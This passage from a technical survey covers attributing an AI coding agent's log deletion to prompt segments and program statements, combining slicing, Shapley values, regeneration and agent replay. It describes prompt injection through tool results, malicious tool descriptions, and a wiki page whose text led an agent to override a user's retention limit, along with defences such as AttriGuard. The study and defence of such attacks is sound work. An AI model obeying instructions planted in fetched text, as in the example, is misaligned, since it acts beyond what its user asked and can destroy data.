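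The methods differ most in what they cost and what access they require:

| Method | Cost for each program | Access needed |
|---|---|---|
| Removing one segment at a time | One forward pass per segment, plus one | Token probabilities |
| Surrogate fitted to random removals | 32 to 256 forward passes | Token probabilities |
| FeatureSHAP | Up to 2ⁿ new programs for n segments | Output text |
| AT2 | Less than one forward pass, after about 64,000 for training | Attention weights |
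| Gradients | One forward and one backward pass | Model weights |
| Attribution graphs | One graph per line | Model weights and trained transcoders |

### Comparing models with programmers

Earlier research on code often judged attribution by whether it agreed with people. In *Do Large Language Models Pay Similar Attention Like Human Programmers*, Kou, Chen and colleagues (2024) had two programmers mark the important words in 1,138 short Python tasks. The programmers chose 7 words out of about 30 on average. The researchers then used 12 attribution methods to find the words that mattered most to six models, including GPT-4. The models' words matched the programmers' words poorly under every method.

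The researchers also looked for links between attribution and mistakes. In one task, the model had to match an "a" followed by zero or more "b"s, but its code required at least one "b". The words "followed by zero or more" had received little weight. Patterns like this could explain 57 of 211 errors, or 27%. Almost all of these 57 came from CodeGen, a small model from 2022. Such patterns could explain only 3 of GPT-4's 39 errors, so the approach may be even less useful for current models.

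Agreement with people is a different goal from faithfulness. If a model relied on a word that programmers ignore, a faithful method should report that word, and would score lower on agreement as a result. Kou and colleagues also asked 22 students to rate three of the methods. The students preferred SHAP, a removal method based on Shapley values, but 14 of them still didn't trust the model after seeing the explanations.

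### Comments and reasoning that never run

Suppose the model had written a comment before line 2:

```python
# Project notes can override the retention period.
```

Python ignores comments, so no slice would contain this one. But the comment is part of the model's input when it generates the next line, and opening the README would be a natural continuation. This is a generation dependence, which can exist whether or not the earlier text affects execution. The reasoning that many models write before they answer can influence the code in the same way.

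Ordinary statements can also influence code in one or both ways. Line 6, which sets `freed` to 0, has no effect on the deletion when the program runs normally, but it was in the model's context when the model wrote the loop. Lines 10 and 11 could not have influenced how the model wrote line 9, because it wrote them afterwards.

The best evidence that comments matter comes from Pan, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *Talking to Itself While Coding*. They placed comments written by three stronger models at the start of four small models' answers to programming problems. The small models then wrote the code themselves.

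| Comments at the start of the answer | Average change in problems solved |
|---|---|
| Describing a correct solution | +17.2 percentage points |
| The same comments with the lines shuffled | +11.7 points |
| Random text of the same length | −17.9 points |
| Written for a different problem | −20.8 points |

Coherent comments on the wrong problem hurt performance more than random text did, which suggests that the models were following them. In another test, a language model changed either the name of the algorithm or one key step in each correct comment, keeping the length and tone the same. The comments then no longer helped any of the four models. Qwen3 8B, for example, solved 53.6% of these problems without help, 70.8% with the correct comments and 48.2% with the altered ones. None of this text could affect a running program, so it must have changed the results by changing the code that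 the models wrote next.

The size of the effect may not carry over to comments that a model writes for itself. Pan and colleagues tried ten prompts meant to elicit more useful comments, and the best recovered only about 24% of the benefit. Across models, the number of comments had no clear link to success. Two models each solved about 81% of the problems, although comments made up 0.1% of one model's output and 71.4% of the other's. A comment in an agent's script is therefore a possible influence that needs testing, since its presence alone doesn't prove that it had an effect.

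Comments also complicate the attribution of the code to the prompt. If an investigator removes W but leaves the comment in place, the probability of lines 2 to 4 may hardly fall, since the comment is enough to prompt the README check. W would seem unimportant even if it was the only reason for the comment. In symbols, where r is a comment or reasoning passage,

p(code | X) = Σ over every possible r of p(r | X) × p(code | X, r).

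Rescoring the recorded code with the recorded comment measures only the last factor. To include the rest, the investigator can either attribute the code to the comment and then the comment to W, or remove W and have the model write everything again, comments included, several times. Cohen-Wang and colleagues tested AT2 on the first step of such a chain, from a final answer back to the reasoning before it, with a 7-billion-parameter reasoning model. AT2 again did about as well as surrogates fitted to many removals. The investigator needs the full text of the reasoning for this step, so it won't work if the provider hides it.

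### Records that link lines to prompts

Some tools skip the estimate and record which conversation a line came from. Albu, Rosa and colleagues (2026), in *Tracybot*, present one for programmers who work with coding agents, and compare it with three others:

| Tool | Each line links to |
|---|---|
| Git AI | The whole agent session |
| Cursor Blame | The whole agent session |
| PromptTrace | The single prompt that introduced the line |
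| Tracybot | The prompts that planned the change and the one that carried it out |

A session may cover many unrelated tasks, and a single prompt may be as uninformative as "go ahead", so Tracybot tries to find the right amount of context between the two. With Claude Code and Codex, it groups the prompt that led to a change with up to five earlier prompts from the same session that changed no files. This is a reasonable rule of thumb, but it could miss an important instruction six prompts back.

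When a person edits the agent's code, Tracybot compares the old and new versions of each changed block using BLEU, a measure of overlapping wording, and still credits the agent if the similarity is above 0.75. This works for formatting changes. But it could wrongly credit the agent if someone changes only the 7 to a 3 in a longer block, because the wording would barely change but the program would delete more files.

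Albu and colleagues showed screenshots of five cases to 24 people, most with two years or less of professional experience. In four of the five cases, over 83% agreed with the tool's attribution. Nobody in the survey used the tool on real work, and agreement doesn't measure whether a prompt influenced a line.

For the log deletion, such a record would link all 11 lines to the user's request U, which mentions 30 days but not 7. W came from a tool, so it might not appear in the record. The record would still help to find the right session, if it existed. When a programmer commits changes, Tracybot keeps only the history of files in that commit, so it would have no record of a script that the agent ran and discarded.

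### Would the whole call survive?

Another coarse method asks whether an agent would still have made a particular tool call if the results of earlier tools had carried less weight. He, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *AttriGuard*, use it to stop prompt injection, an attack in which someone hides instructions in text that an agent will read. They define the effect of the tool results on a call c as

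log p(c) − log p₀(c),

where p is the probability of the call given the full results, and p₀ is its probability given results that provide the same facts but no longer steer the agent. This is the same kind of drop as before, with a whole call as the output and all the tool results together as the segment.

Many commercial models don't reveal these probabilities, so AttriGuard looks at whether the call survives:

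1. Before the agent's call runs, a language model rewrites the earlier tool results. It turns structured data into plain sentences and commands into descriptions, so an order to send a report becomes a neutral remark that the text asks for this. A stricter setting also weakens stated reasons.
2. The agent chooses its next action again from the rewritten results. Its own past actions stay the same, so small differences can't build up over several steps.
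3. If the new choice includes the same tool with the same arguments, the call goes ahead. If only the arguments differ, another model judges whether the original call fits the user's request. If the tool is missing, AttriGuard blocks the call.

On AgentDojo, none of four standard types of attack succeeded against Gemini 2.5 Flash or Llama 3.3 70B with AttriGuard in place. Without it, an average of 16.9% succeeded against Gemini and 15.5% against Llama. Attackers who knew how the defence worked and had 200 attempts per case succeeded in 6.6% of cases against Gemini and 9.8% against Llama. AttriGuard made runs take about three times as long and roughly doubled token use with Llama.

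The rewriting has to be strong enough to stop attacks. When He and colleagues only turned structured data into sentences, 12.2% of one type of attack got through. AttriGuard also reduced the number of harmless tasks Llama completed by about 20% on long travel bookings, which needed up to 18 calls. This happened because Llama's choices varied from one run to the next even without an attack, and AttriGuard misclassified some of this variation as outside influence.

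In the log example, the call under test would be the whole program. With a weaker version of W, the agent might still write a program to delete old logs, but with a limit of 30 days and no README check. The judge would then decide whether the original program was consistent with U, and might well approve it. The test is better at detecting a call with no basis in the user's request than at explaining one line of a mostly reasonable program.

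### Where attribution goes wrong

Redundant text causes problems for every method based on removal. Suppose the agent's standing instructions also contain a rule to check project notes, and either that rule or W is enough to produce the README check. In a second case, the model needs both, perhaps because W mentions an override and the rule explains where to find it. In both cases, 1 means that the check appears and 0 means that it doesn't.

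| | Drop without W | Drop without the rule | Drop without both | Shapley values |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Either one is enough | 0 | 0 | 1 | ½ each |
| The model needs both | 1 | 1 | 1 | ½ each |

Removing one segment at a time makes both segments look irrelevant in the first case and gives each full credit in the second. Shapley values and a surrogate fitted to random removals both split the credit equally in each case, even though deleting W from the prompt would save `worker.log` only in the second. An investigator therefore has to remove suspected duplicates both separately and together. Agents create many duplicates by repeating parts of a document in their notes.

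Removing text can also produce a prompt unlike anything the model normally sees. If the text of W disappears but the request to fetch it remains, the model may try to fetch the page again, which makes the original program less likely for a reason unrelated to retention periods. Deleting "older" from U leaves the ungrammatical "delete logs than 30 days". Kou and colleagues note that deletion can change the meaning of an input, and one of the 12 methods they tested replaces each word with a likely alternative instead. AT2 is trained on removals that leave the text in place but block the model's attention to it.

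Shilpika, Graziani and colleagues (2026), in *Probabilistic Attribution For Large Language Models*, avoid removal by averaging over everything a token could have been. If the original token at some position is t, its score is the logarithm of

p(Y | X) ÷ Σ over every token t′ of p(Y | X with t′ in place of t) × p(t′ | the rest of X).

Likely replacements get more weight than unlikely ones, so the comparison is mostly with prompts that make sense. The exact sum has a term for every token in the vocabulary, and a whole wiki page has far too many possible replacements to average over. A practical alternative would be to write a few realistic versions of the page without the sentence about README files.

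Closed models are the most common obstacle. Shilpika and colleagues point out that token probabilities are easy to get from a model that runs locally, but not through a chatbot or a company's interface. Esmaeili gives the same reason for TokenScope's limited use with such models. Without these probabilities, the investigator has to compare programs written with and without W. If the share that check the README falls from 90% to 10%, fewer than ten programs of each kind are usually enough to detect the change. Telling 20% from 5% takes about 75 of each by the usual statistical standards, and the investigator would have to repeat the comparison for every suspected segment. Running the prompt through an open model and using its probabilities instead would show what influences that model, which may not be what influenced the agent.

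## Joining program analysis and prompt attribution

Slicing traces the deletion of `worker.log` back to lines 2 to 4 and the README. Prompt attribution traces the program back to the wiki page W and the user's request U. The program text connects the two results, but slicing produces a list of statements and prompt attribution produces a set of scores. An investigator can combine them by scoring only the statements in the slice, by generating the program again and comparing what the new versions do, or by dividing the credit between texts that affect the outcome at different points in the chain. The probabilities in the log example below are illustrative, not measured.

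### Scoring only the lines in the slice

The log-probability of a program is a sum over its tokens, so an investigator can add up the terms for some lines and ignore the others. For a set of lines L, the drop from removing a segment s of the prompt X is

drop(s, L) = Σ over tokens yᵢ in L of [log p(yᵢ | X, y₁, …, yᵢ₋₁) − log p(yᵢ | X without s, y₁, …, yᵢ₋₁)].

The slice supplies L. The dynamic slice for `worker.log` has seven lines, but the user wants to know why 12 days was old enough, so the value to trace is `days` on line 8. Its dynamic slice is lines 2 to 4. Suppose the scores come out like this:

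| Segment removed | Drop on lines 2 to 4 | Drop on the other eight lines | Drop on the whole program |
|---|---|---|---|
| W | 3 | 1 | 4 |
| U | 0.5 | 20 | 20.5 |

When attribution covers the whole program, U ranks first by a factor of five. That is a sensible answer to why the agent wrote a script for deleting logs, since it had no reason to without the request. But the user is asking about the override of the 30-day limit, and on those lines W's drop is six times U's. W made lines 2 to 4 about 20 times as likely (e³), compared with about 1.6 times for U.

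These scores treat the earlier part of the program as given. Cohen-Wang and colleagues note that one can attribute any span of a model's output, treating everything before it as input. Line 1 and any comment above lines 2 to 4 are then possible influences, even though the slice leaves them out. An analyst should therefore use the slice to choose which lines to explain, but not to exclude earlier text that may have influenced them.

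Matching tokens to lines also takes some care because, as Esmaeili points out, a model's tokens don't generally line up with the units of a programming language. One token might contain the colon that ends line 3, the line break, and the indentation of line 4. TokenScope treats a token as a candidate for any unit it overlaps, so anyone summing over several lines has to count each token only once.

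Some errors remain however well the slice fits. Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Sightline*, prove several limits on attribution and check the proofs by computer. One concerns tokens that the model is almost certain about. If a token has probability p, the gradient of its log-probability is at most

√2 × (1 − p) × ‖J‖,

where J describes how strongly the segment can shift the model's raw scores for the next token. As p approaches 1, the gradient disappears, even if the segment is the reason for the certainty. Removal has a similar problem when the token stays likely without the segment. If its probability is at least m in both cases, its log-probability can change by no more than (1 − m)/m, which is about 0.01 for m = 0.99. The 7 on line 4 is probably a token of this kind, which is a reason to score the whole slice and not that token alone.

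The slice doesn't help with duplicated text. Xu and colleagues inserted two extra copies of a value into several hundred prompts and tested whether each method could tell the original from an irrelevant passage. The AUROC for removing one passage at a time fell from 93–97% to 54–69%, where 50% is chance. Their own method, which uses attention, stayed at 99% or above.

### Generating the program again

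The drop in log-probability explains the exact text that the model wrote. The model could have reached the same deletion with different text, for example by extracting the number from the README with a pattern instead of looking for a fixed phrase. To measure the influence of a segment on the deletion itself, the investigator can sum over every program c that the model might write:

effect(s) = Σ over c of [p(c | X) − p(c | X without s)] × Y(c).

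Y(c) is 1 if c deletes `worker.log` when it runs on the recorded README and list of files, and 0 otherwise. Nobody can list every possible program, so the model writes a sample with each prompt. Suppose it writes 100 programs with W in the prompt, of which 80 contain the override, and 100 without W, of which 4 do. If every program with the override deletes `worker.log` and no other program does, the estimated effect of W is 0.80 − 0.04 = 0.76, with a 95% confidence interval from about 0.67 to 0.85.

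This figure includes any influence W had through comments and reasoning. The method works on closed models, but it requires generating 200 new programs for one segment and running them all with stand-ins for their tools.

With path conditions, the investigator can use the same sample to find the effect of W on logs of any age, without running the programs again for each log. Suppose symbolic execution shows that the programs with the override delete logs older than 7 days when the phrase is present, and that the rest delete logs older than 30 days. The effect of W is then 0.76 for every log from 8 to 30 days old and zero for all others, including the 45-day-old log.

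They also make it possible to group programs that behave alike. Sharma and David (2025), in *Assessing Correctness in LLM-Based Code Generation via Uncertainty Estimation*, do this to judge how sure a model is of its code:

1. The model writes several programs for the same prompt.
2. Each program that doesn't run goes into a group of its own.
3. A symbolic execution engine collects the path conditions of the others, along with formulas for their variables.
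4. Two programs join the same group if the engine finds no input on which they differ, up to a fixed depth.
5. The probability of a group is the sum of the probabilities of its programs.

In one example, three programs with different code counted passengers over 60, and they formed one group with a probability of 1. Three programs from a weaker model each read the age from a different wrong place, so they formed three groups.

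Step 5 is difficult because whole programs have tiny probabilities. Those three equivalent programs had log-probabilities between −582 and −625, so their probabilities are too small for ordinary arithmetic. Sharma and David tried adjusting for length and tried giving each sampled program equal weight, and the two methods worked about equally well. Counting "80 of 100" already weights the programs equally.

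For the log deletion, suppose that 60 of the 80 programs look for the phrase "retention: 7" and the other 20 read whatever number follows "retention:". Both kinds delete `worker.log`, so they count equally towards the 0.76. But if the README says "retention: 70", the first kind still match their phrase and lower the limit to 7, while the second kind raise it to 70. An engine that treats the README text as unknown could separate them. This difference doesn't affect the explanation of this accident, but it matters to someone who wants to prevent the next one.

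Running all the programs on the same inputs is a way to group them that takes less computation. *Using Semantic Distance to Estimate Uncertainty in LLM-Based Code Generation* (2026) puts two programs in the same group if they give identical outcomes on every input, including the type of any error. This would put all 80 programs in one group unless one of the inputs contained a phrase like "retention: 70". The inputs from a concolic run of the original program would be a good starting set, since they cover both outcomes of its tests.

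*Predictive Prompt Analysis* (2025) tries to avoid most of the sampling by predicting how a prompt changes the frequency of a given code structure. However, it predicts syntax rather than effects, and an `if` that checks the README has the same structure as any other `if`.

For agents that call tools directly, *AgentSentry* (2026) computes a similar difference. When a tool returns a result, it estimates how likely the agent is to propose its next action given the original context. It then repeats the estimate with the user's request masked, or with suspicious content removed from the tool results, and takes the difference. Counting identical actions is reasonable for a call with two or three arguments, but an agent rarely writes the same program twice, so the formula above needs Y(c).

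### Credit for the wiki page and the README

Neither formula gives the README any credit, because it was not in the prompt. W affects which program the model writes and the README affects what that program does, so the investigator has to vary both:

| W in the prompt | Phrase in the README | Probability of deleting `worker.log` |
|---|---|---|
| Yes | Yes | 0.80 |
| No | Yes | 0.04 |
| Yes | No | 0 |
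| No | No | 0 |

Each entry is v = Σ over c of p(c | prompt) × Y(c, README). The investigator can compute the bottom two rows without new programs, either by running the same 200 with a README that lacks the phrase or by setting the phrase to absent in their path conditions.

Removing W lowers the probability by 0.76 and removing the phrase lowers it by 0.80. These add up to 1.56, almost twice the total there is to explain, because the deletion usually needs both. Shapley values average over the two orders in which the texts could join:

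- W: ½ × (0 − 0) + ½ × (0.80 − 0.04) = 0.38
- README: ½ × (0.04 − 0) + ½ × (0.80 − 0) = 0.42

The README's share is slightly larger because 4% of programs check it even without W. The shares add up to 0.80 rather than 1 because they describe how likely this situation was to end in a deletion. In the recorded run the deletion did happen, partly because the model happened to write one of the 80 programs rather than one of the other 20.

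Shares like these depend on which items are on the list. If the request U is added, and the agent never deletes anything without U, the shares become 0.25 for W, 0.27 for the README and 0.27 for U. W's share has dropped by a third, although its influence has not changed. The 0.76 is the estimated benefit of removing W, so it is the better number for deciding whether to edit the wiki page. Shapley shares are more useful for a report that has to divide responsibility without double counting.

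The calculation also assumes that the README can affect the deletion by only one route. If an earlier step had printed the file, the model would have read it before writing the program. Removing the phrase would then require generating new programs as well as rerunning the old ones without it.

*Explaining a Series of Models by Propagating Shapley Values* (2021) gives a method for passing Shapley values through a chain of models. The method divides the last model's output among its inputs, then divides each share among the inputs of the model before, and so on back to the original data. The models can be of different types, such as a neural network followed by a set of decision trees, as long as the shares at each stage add up to that stage's output. These models pass numbers to each other, whereas a language model passes on a program. The presence of lines 2 to 4 is not a quantity that the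 next stage can split in proportion, so the table above has to treat the two stages together.

### Gradients through program operations

When a program passes numbers from one operation to the next, an analysis can measure influence inside it without trying many inputs. Dynamic taint analysis, the usual tool for following data through a run, marks chosen inputs and every value computed from them. Each mark is either present or absent, so it doesn't measure how strong the influence is. *Fine Grained Dataflow Tracking with Proximal Gradients* (Ryan, Shah and colleagues, 2019) gives the example of a program that adds `a * 8` to `b / 8`. Taint analysis marks the sum as depending on both inputs, although a change to `a` has a much larger effect than the same change to `b`.

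Their method, proximal gradient analysis, replaces the marks with gradients. For smooth functions, the chain rule gives the slope of a whole calculation from the slopes of its steps: (f ∘ g)′(x) = f′(g(x)) × g′(x). Programs are full of operations with no slope in the ordinary sense, such as taking a remainder or comparing bits. For these, the method looks at nearby points and picks the y that minimises

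−|f(x) − f(y)| + ½(x − y)².

The first part favours a point where the result changes a lot, and the second a point close to x. The slope of the line from x to the chosen point then replaces the derivative. In practice the tool tries up to five points and uses the derivative from the previous operation to set the distance between them.

Suppose a program multiplies an input by 2 and then takes the remainder after dividing by 4. Starting from zero, the tool tries 2, 4, 6 and so on, gets remainders of 2, 0, 2, and reports a slope of 1 across the remainder operation. If the program multiplies by 4 instead, the tool tries 4, 8, 12 and so on, and every remainder is 0. The derivative is correctly 0, because no input can change the result. Taint analysis would normally report a dependence in both cases.

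Ryan and colleagues tested this method on seven programs that read files, such as a JPEG decoder. They changed each byte of the input to find out which bytes affected the values in the program's tests. The average F1 score was 0.70, compared with 0.50 for the best taint tracker, and the largest gain was about 33 percentage points. The gain came from fewer false alarms. On all seven programs, the new method found a smaller share of the true dependences than the taint tracker did, so it would be a poor basis for ruling out a dependence. Running time rose by 3.2% on average and 21.7% at worst, on top of the time added by taint tracking. The tool also helped find 22 bugs, of which developers confirmed 20.

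Gradients would suit an agent's script that calculates its limit. If the README said "weeks: 1" and line 4 were `days = weeks * 7`, the derivative of `days` with respect to that number would be 7. But line 4 actually sets a constant, and the README matters only because of the test on line 3. The method analyzes only the path that ran, so it sets the derivative to 0 when a nearby point would send the program down a different branch. It would therefore find no influence of the README on the deletion. Ryan and colleagues excluded influence through branches from their accuracy test because neither method can detect it.

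The method also takes the program as fixed. W had its effect by adding three lines, and no value inside the program rises or falls with W. One can still write down a gradient for the whole chain by differentiating the probability of deletion with respect to the numbers xᵢ that represent a token of the prompt:

∂/∂xᵢ Σ over c of p(c | X) × Y(c) = Σ over c of p(c | X) × Y(c) × ∂ log p(c | X)/∂xᵢ.

This is the model's own gradient, averaged over programs and counting only those that delete the log. It doesn't require differentiating the program, so it works even when the effect is binary. But it needs a sample of programs, and it has the same weakness as other gradients on tokens the model predicts with high confidence.

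### Replaying the steps of an agent

Writing a program is only one step in an agent's run, and a different step may have determined the outcome. *Causal Agent Replay* treats a run as a chain of causes and changes one step at a time. It can resample an action from the same model, force a particular action, replace a tool's result, edit the history or switch to another model. The agent then makes all its later decisions again. Because these decisions vary by chance, the system repeats the run many times and reports how often it ends badly, with a confidence interval.

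In the log example, regenerating the program with everything else unchanged leads to a deletion 80% of the time. Replacing the text of W with a page that has no such rule lowers this to 4%. The difference is the same 0.76 as before, so the regeneration method is one case of this broader scheme.

Resampling an early step also reruns every later step, so an irrelevant early step seems to have an effect whenever a decisive step comes after it. *Causal Agent Replay* therefore picks the latest step whose effect is clearly different from zero and calls it the point of commitment, after which a new decision no longer rescues the run. For failures that need two steps to go wrong together, the system estimates Shapley values over steps. In an artificial test with a known answer, it gave the two responsible steps 0.44 and 0.45, and the total of 0.909 almost matched the true value of 0.91. The demonstrations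 all used simulated tools.

Mahale uses an artificial four-step run to examine what such effects can mean. Step 1 retrieves a value that is 0 or 1 with equal probability. Step 3 is a tool call that copies this value 90% of the time and flips it otherwise. The outcome is the average of the values from steps 1 and 3. Steps 0 and 2 are connected to nothing. In the run to be explained, the retrieval returned 1, the tool call copied it, and the outcome was 1. The table gives the average change in the outcome when each step is redrawn.

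| Step | Later steps decide afresh | Later steps reuse their random draws | Later steps repeat their actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0: connected to nothing | −0.50 | 0 | 0 |
| 1: retrieval | −0.50 | −0.50 | −0.25 |
| 2: connected to nothing | −0.05 | 0 | 0 |
| 3: tool call | −0.05 | −0.05 | −0.05 |

In the first column of results, the inert step 0 has exactly the same effect as the decisive retrieval, because drawing step 0 again also lets the retrieval change. Mahale proves that this is true for every possible run of the chain, so no threshold or number of repetitions can distinguish the two.

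Reusing the later steps' random draws fixes this, and the effects of the inert steps drop to exactly zero. However, the decisive step can also get zero, so an effect of zero doesn't prove that a step did nothing. In one run out of ten, the tool call reverses the retrieved value. The outcome is then ½ regardless of what the retrieval returns, because one half of the average goes up when the other goes down. If the tool call instead repeats its recorded action, the retrieval has an effect of 0.25 in these runs.

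Subtracting the last column from the one before it gives the part of the effect that passed through later decisions. Mahale shows why this part shouldn't be reported as a percentage, such as how much of W's influence went through a comment. In a variant of the chain where the two routes oppose each other, the total effect is 0.30, the direct part is −0.10 and the indirect part is 0.40, so the indirect "share" is 133%.

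Reusing random draws is also difficult with real models, because the same draw can pick a different token once the context has changed. How often the two choices match depends on how the software pairs them. When two sets of token probabilities differ by 0.18 in total variation distance, the best possible pairing gives the same token 82% of the time. Reusing the draw gave the same token 41% of the time in a test with 32 tokens, and 0.4% of the time in the worst case with 100,000 tokens. These tests used artificial probabilities, and nobody has tried the estimators on a live agent.

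The step identified also depends on which question is asked. Mahale compared the point-of-commitment rule with the largest effect under reused draws on 60 runs of the chain, and the two methods selected different steps in 52. The rule selects the tool call, after which nothing could change the outcome, while the effect measure selects the retrieval, which supplied the value. For the log deletion, the same disagreement could arise between the step that wrote the program and the step that fetched W.

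None of these experiments examines the steps inside the program. Drawing a step again works only if the step could have come out differently. When Mahale made the tool call copy the retrieved value every time, all three measures gave it an effect of zero, although half of the outcome still came through it. Mahale calls this "the absence of a measurement". The same problem arises with a finished program. With the same README and files, line 3 gives the same result on every run, so drawing it again doesn't measure its importance. Replacing a tool result doesn't help either if the system can only replace results that went to the agent, because the README's text went to the program.

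Slicing covers this part of the chain. Steps 0 and 2 are inert because no path leads from them to the outcome, and Mahale knew this only because he had built the chain. A dependence graph gives the same information about real code. Without repeated runs, it shows that nothing leads from line 6 to the deletion as long as no statement fails. It also shows which values are worth changing. The investigator can then change the README and measure the effect, which the slice alone can't give.

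### Systems that cover part of the chain

No published system appears to trace a passage in the prompt through the statements of a generated program to an outside effect. The closest systems combine program analysis with model calls, but they analyse the program that calls the model, not the program the model writes.

*Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) presents PRISM, which supplies the missing rule for how data passes through a model call. Language models compare each input of the call with the output and choose from 25 labels, such as a translation, a summary, a single decision or no visible trace. An ordinary slicer then leaves out the code that produced any input labelled as leaving no visible trace. In the variant of the log program that gets the retention period from a model, PRISM could conclude that the answer "7" reflects the README but not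 the user's 30 days.

In files where the model had ignored some input, this removed 23% of the lines from slices on average, and a manual check found no lost dependences. For tracking untrusted data, PRISM had an F1 score of 81.7%, compared with 62.8% for the best alternative and 47.5% for assuming that every input reaches the output. These figures depend on judging whether the output visibly reflects an input, so a passage that changed the model's choice without leaving a visible trace could get the wrong label.

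Sightline addresses the same question using the model's attention. Models also attend to text they don't use, so Sightline learns from labelled examples which attention patterns indicate that the model used an input. It then sets a threshold so that it misses a share of true dependences chosen by the user, such as 1%. On applications it had not seen before, the 1% setting removed 44% to 66% of the false dependences and took at most 0.2 seconds per call. The 1% is an average over many calls, so it gives no assurance about any single deletion.

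Sightline may also work on closed models. Xu and colleagues had each of four small open models read the outputs of the other three, and this worked about as well as having each model read its own. However, this test only simulated closed models, and all four were much smaller than the models behind today's agents.

If the call outputs an eleven-line program, both systems would report only that W reached the program as a whole. Sightline could probably check lines 2 to 4 separately, because it records attention for each output token, but it would need new labelled examples to set a threshold for single statements.

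Other systems connect the prompt to a tool call but don't analyze the code that the call runs. *MindGuard* (2025) builds a graph modelled on the program dependence graph, with edges based on attention, to find out whether a malicious tool description led to a call. *AgentTracer* (2026) links successive calls by searching the agent's written reasoning for the results that informed each decision. AttriGuard, by He and colleagues, *AgentArmor* and AgentFlow, by Wang and colleagues, also stop at the tool call. All of these systems would treat the log program as a single action, so they could not show why it deleted a 12-day-old log.

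### Slices that guide a model's attention

It is also possible to go from the slice to the model. Rong, Yadavally and Nguyen (2026), in *Post-hoc Attention Steering of Large Language Models for Robust Code Understanding*, use slices to help a model read code that someone has deliberately made confusing. Their tool, CodeSteer, keeps the statements that both depend on the program's input and affect its output, together with the tests that control them. It gives the tokens of these statements a higher weight p(k), and then changes how much selected attention heads attend to each token k:

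new attention to k ∝ old attention to k × (p(k) + ε)^β.

Here β sets the strength of the change, and ε is a small constant that keeps the weight above zero.

The task was to judge whether statements about a Java program's output were true. On one set of programs, the confusing versions lowered a 7-billion-parameter model's accuracy from 76.5% to 64.0%, and steering raised it to 77.4%. Across four models and two sets of programs, steering recovered 28% to 107% of the lost accuracy. Telling the model in the prompt which tokens mattered was usually much less effective.

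These results suggest that a model can use the text that a slice picks out, and that the slice's statements can be mapped onto tokens well enough for an intervention. They don't show what the model relied on before the steering. The slicer also succeeded on only 152 of 820 programs with 300 to 600 lines, and a joined analysis of long agent scripts could run into the same limit.

### Programs whose output carries its sources

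An agent could make the join easier by moving more of its decisions into code. *GenerationPrograms* (Wan, Hirsch and colleagues, 2025) does this for question answering. The model writes a short program that paraphrases, shortens, merges or copies numbered sentences from the source documents, and running the program produces the answer. The program shows which source sentences went into each sentence of the answer, much as a small dynamic slice would, and the answer cites them.

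Wan and colleagues compared this with having the same model write its own citations, and measured how well the cited sentences supported the answer.

| Set of questions | Method | Citation quality (F1) | Match with the reference answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| ASQA | Model writes its own citations | 54.2 | 42.3 |
| ASQA | *GenerationPrograms* | 79.4 | 41.0 |
| LFQA | Model writes its own citations | 54.0 | 39.9 |
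| LFQA | *GenerationPrograms* | 82.8 | 32.3 |

Citations improved a lot on both sets. Answers matched the reference almost as well on ASQA but noticeably less well on LFQA, although human raters saw a smaller difference.

The method can also work backwards from a finished answer, by having the model write a program that could have produced it. The resulting citations matched those of human annotators with an F1 score of 47.4, compared with 7.8 when a model just named the sources. For an investigation, though, such a program is only a plausible reconstruction, because the model may have produced the original answer in some other way.

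An agent that cleans up logs could borrow the idea by storing each setting with its source. If line 3 had taken the words "retention: 7" from a variable that held the relevant sentence of W, a slice of the deletion would have led to the wiki page as well as the README. The slice still wouldn't show why the model chose that sentence. *GenerationPrograms* has the same limitation, because the model picks its source sentences while it writes the program, before there is a run to trace. A model that had learned in training to check README files might cite W even if it would have written the same program without W, so the investigator would still have to remove W and see whether the override disappears.

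## Testing whether a trace is right

An investigator can check a finished trace in several ways, such as removing W and looking for the override. The trace of the `worker.log` deletion implies what should happen if the program, the README or the prompt changes, so the investigator can change each one and compare the result with the prediction. Testing a change to the program takes one run, but testing a change to the prompt takes many, because the model may write a different program each time.

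### Changing the program

The investigator should first run the original program on the recorded README and file list, with a harmless stand-in for `delete`. If this run doesn't reproduce the recorded deletions, the replay is faulty and the other checks are of little use. It also helps to compare intermediate values as well as the outcome. In Pakhomov and Nijkamp's experiment, up to 20 of 24 restored runs diverged from the original, but the final score never changed, so checking only the outcome would have missed the divergence.

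The next step is to run the slice alone on the same input and check that it makes the same deletions. The step after that is to change lines inside and outside the slice. The table shows the expected results for the first five logs, which are 3, 45, 2, 20 and 12 days old.

| Version | Ages of the logs it deletes |
|---|---|
| Original program | 45, 20, 12 |
| Slice alone (lines 2–5 and 7–9) | 45, 20, 12 |
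| Line 4 sets the limit to 12 | 45, 20 |
| README lacks the phrase | 45 |
| Line 1 sets the limit to 90 | 45, 20, 12 |
| Line 6 sets `freed` to 100 | 45, 20, 12 |
| Line 6 sets `freed` to the text "0" | 45, then an error |

A change to a sliced line has to be large enough to affect the result. If the limit is raised from 7 to 8 days, the program will still delete a 12-day-old log, but this doesn't show that the trace is wrong. The tester should also make these changes in the full program, because the slice alone stops with an error if the README lacks the phrase.

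The last row is consistent with the trace, even though line 6 is outside the slice and changing it saved `worker.log`. The slice excludes line 6 only on the assumption that no statement fails, and this change made line 10 fail. A good report would state that assumption next to the slice.

### Why a few matching runs are not enough

Agreement on five logs is weak evidence that two programs always behave alike. Suppose the investigator has a model tidy up the slice, and the model changes `f.age > days` to `f.age >= days`. The new version deletes the same three logs, because the change only affects logs exactly as old as the limit, and the five include no such log.

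*A Differential Fuzzing-Based Evaluation of Functional Equivalence in LLM-Generated Code Refactorings* (Dristi and Dwyer, 2026) measures how often this kind of difference goes unnoticed. Dristi and Dwyer told six models to simplify or speed up Python code from three standard collections, and to return the code unchanged if no safe edit was possible. They then checked the results with differential fuzzing, which meant running the old and new versions on 1,000 or 2,000 automatically generated inputs and counting them as equivalent only if every output matched.

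After Dristi and Dwyer removed code that timed out or didn't compile, 3,538 rewrites remained. Depending on the model, 19% to 35% behaved differently from the original. In total, 933 rewrites were faulty, and 202 of them (about 22%) passed every test that came with their collection. Having more tests did not help, perhaps because many of the extra tests exercised the same paths. The tests missed 22.4% of the faulty rewrites in the collection with an average of 21 tests per problem, and 21.6% in the one with three. GPT-4o did best of the six models. Current models would probably make fewer mistakes, but the tests would be no better at catching those that remain.

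Fuzzing can miss differences too, because it only samples inputs. For a program as simple as the log script, a constraint solver is better. It would find almost immediately that the two versions disagree at an age of 7. If it showed instead that no age made them disagree on any path, the investigator could treat them as equivalent for this purpose.

### Regenerating without the wiki page

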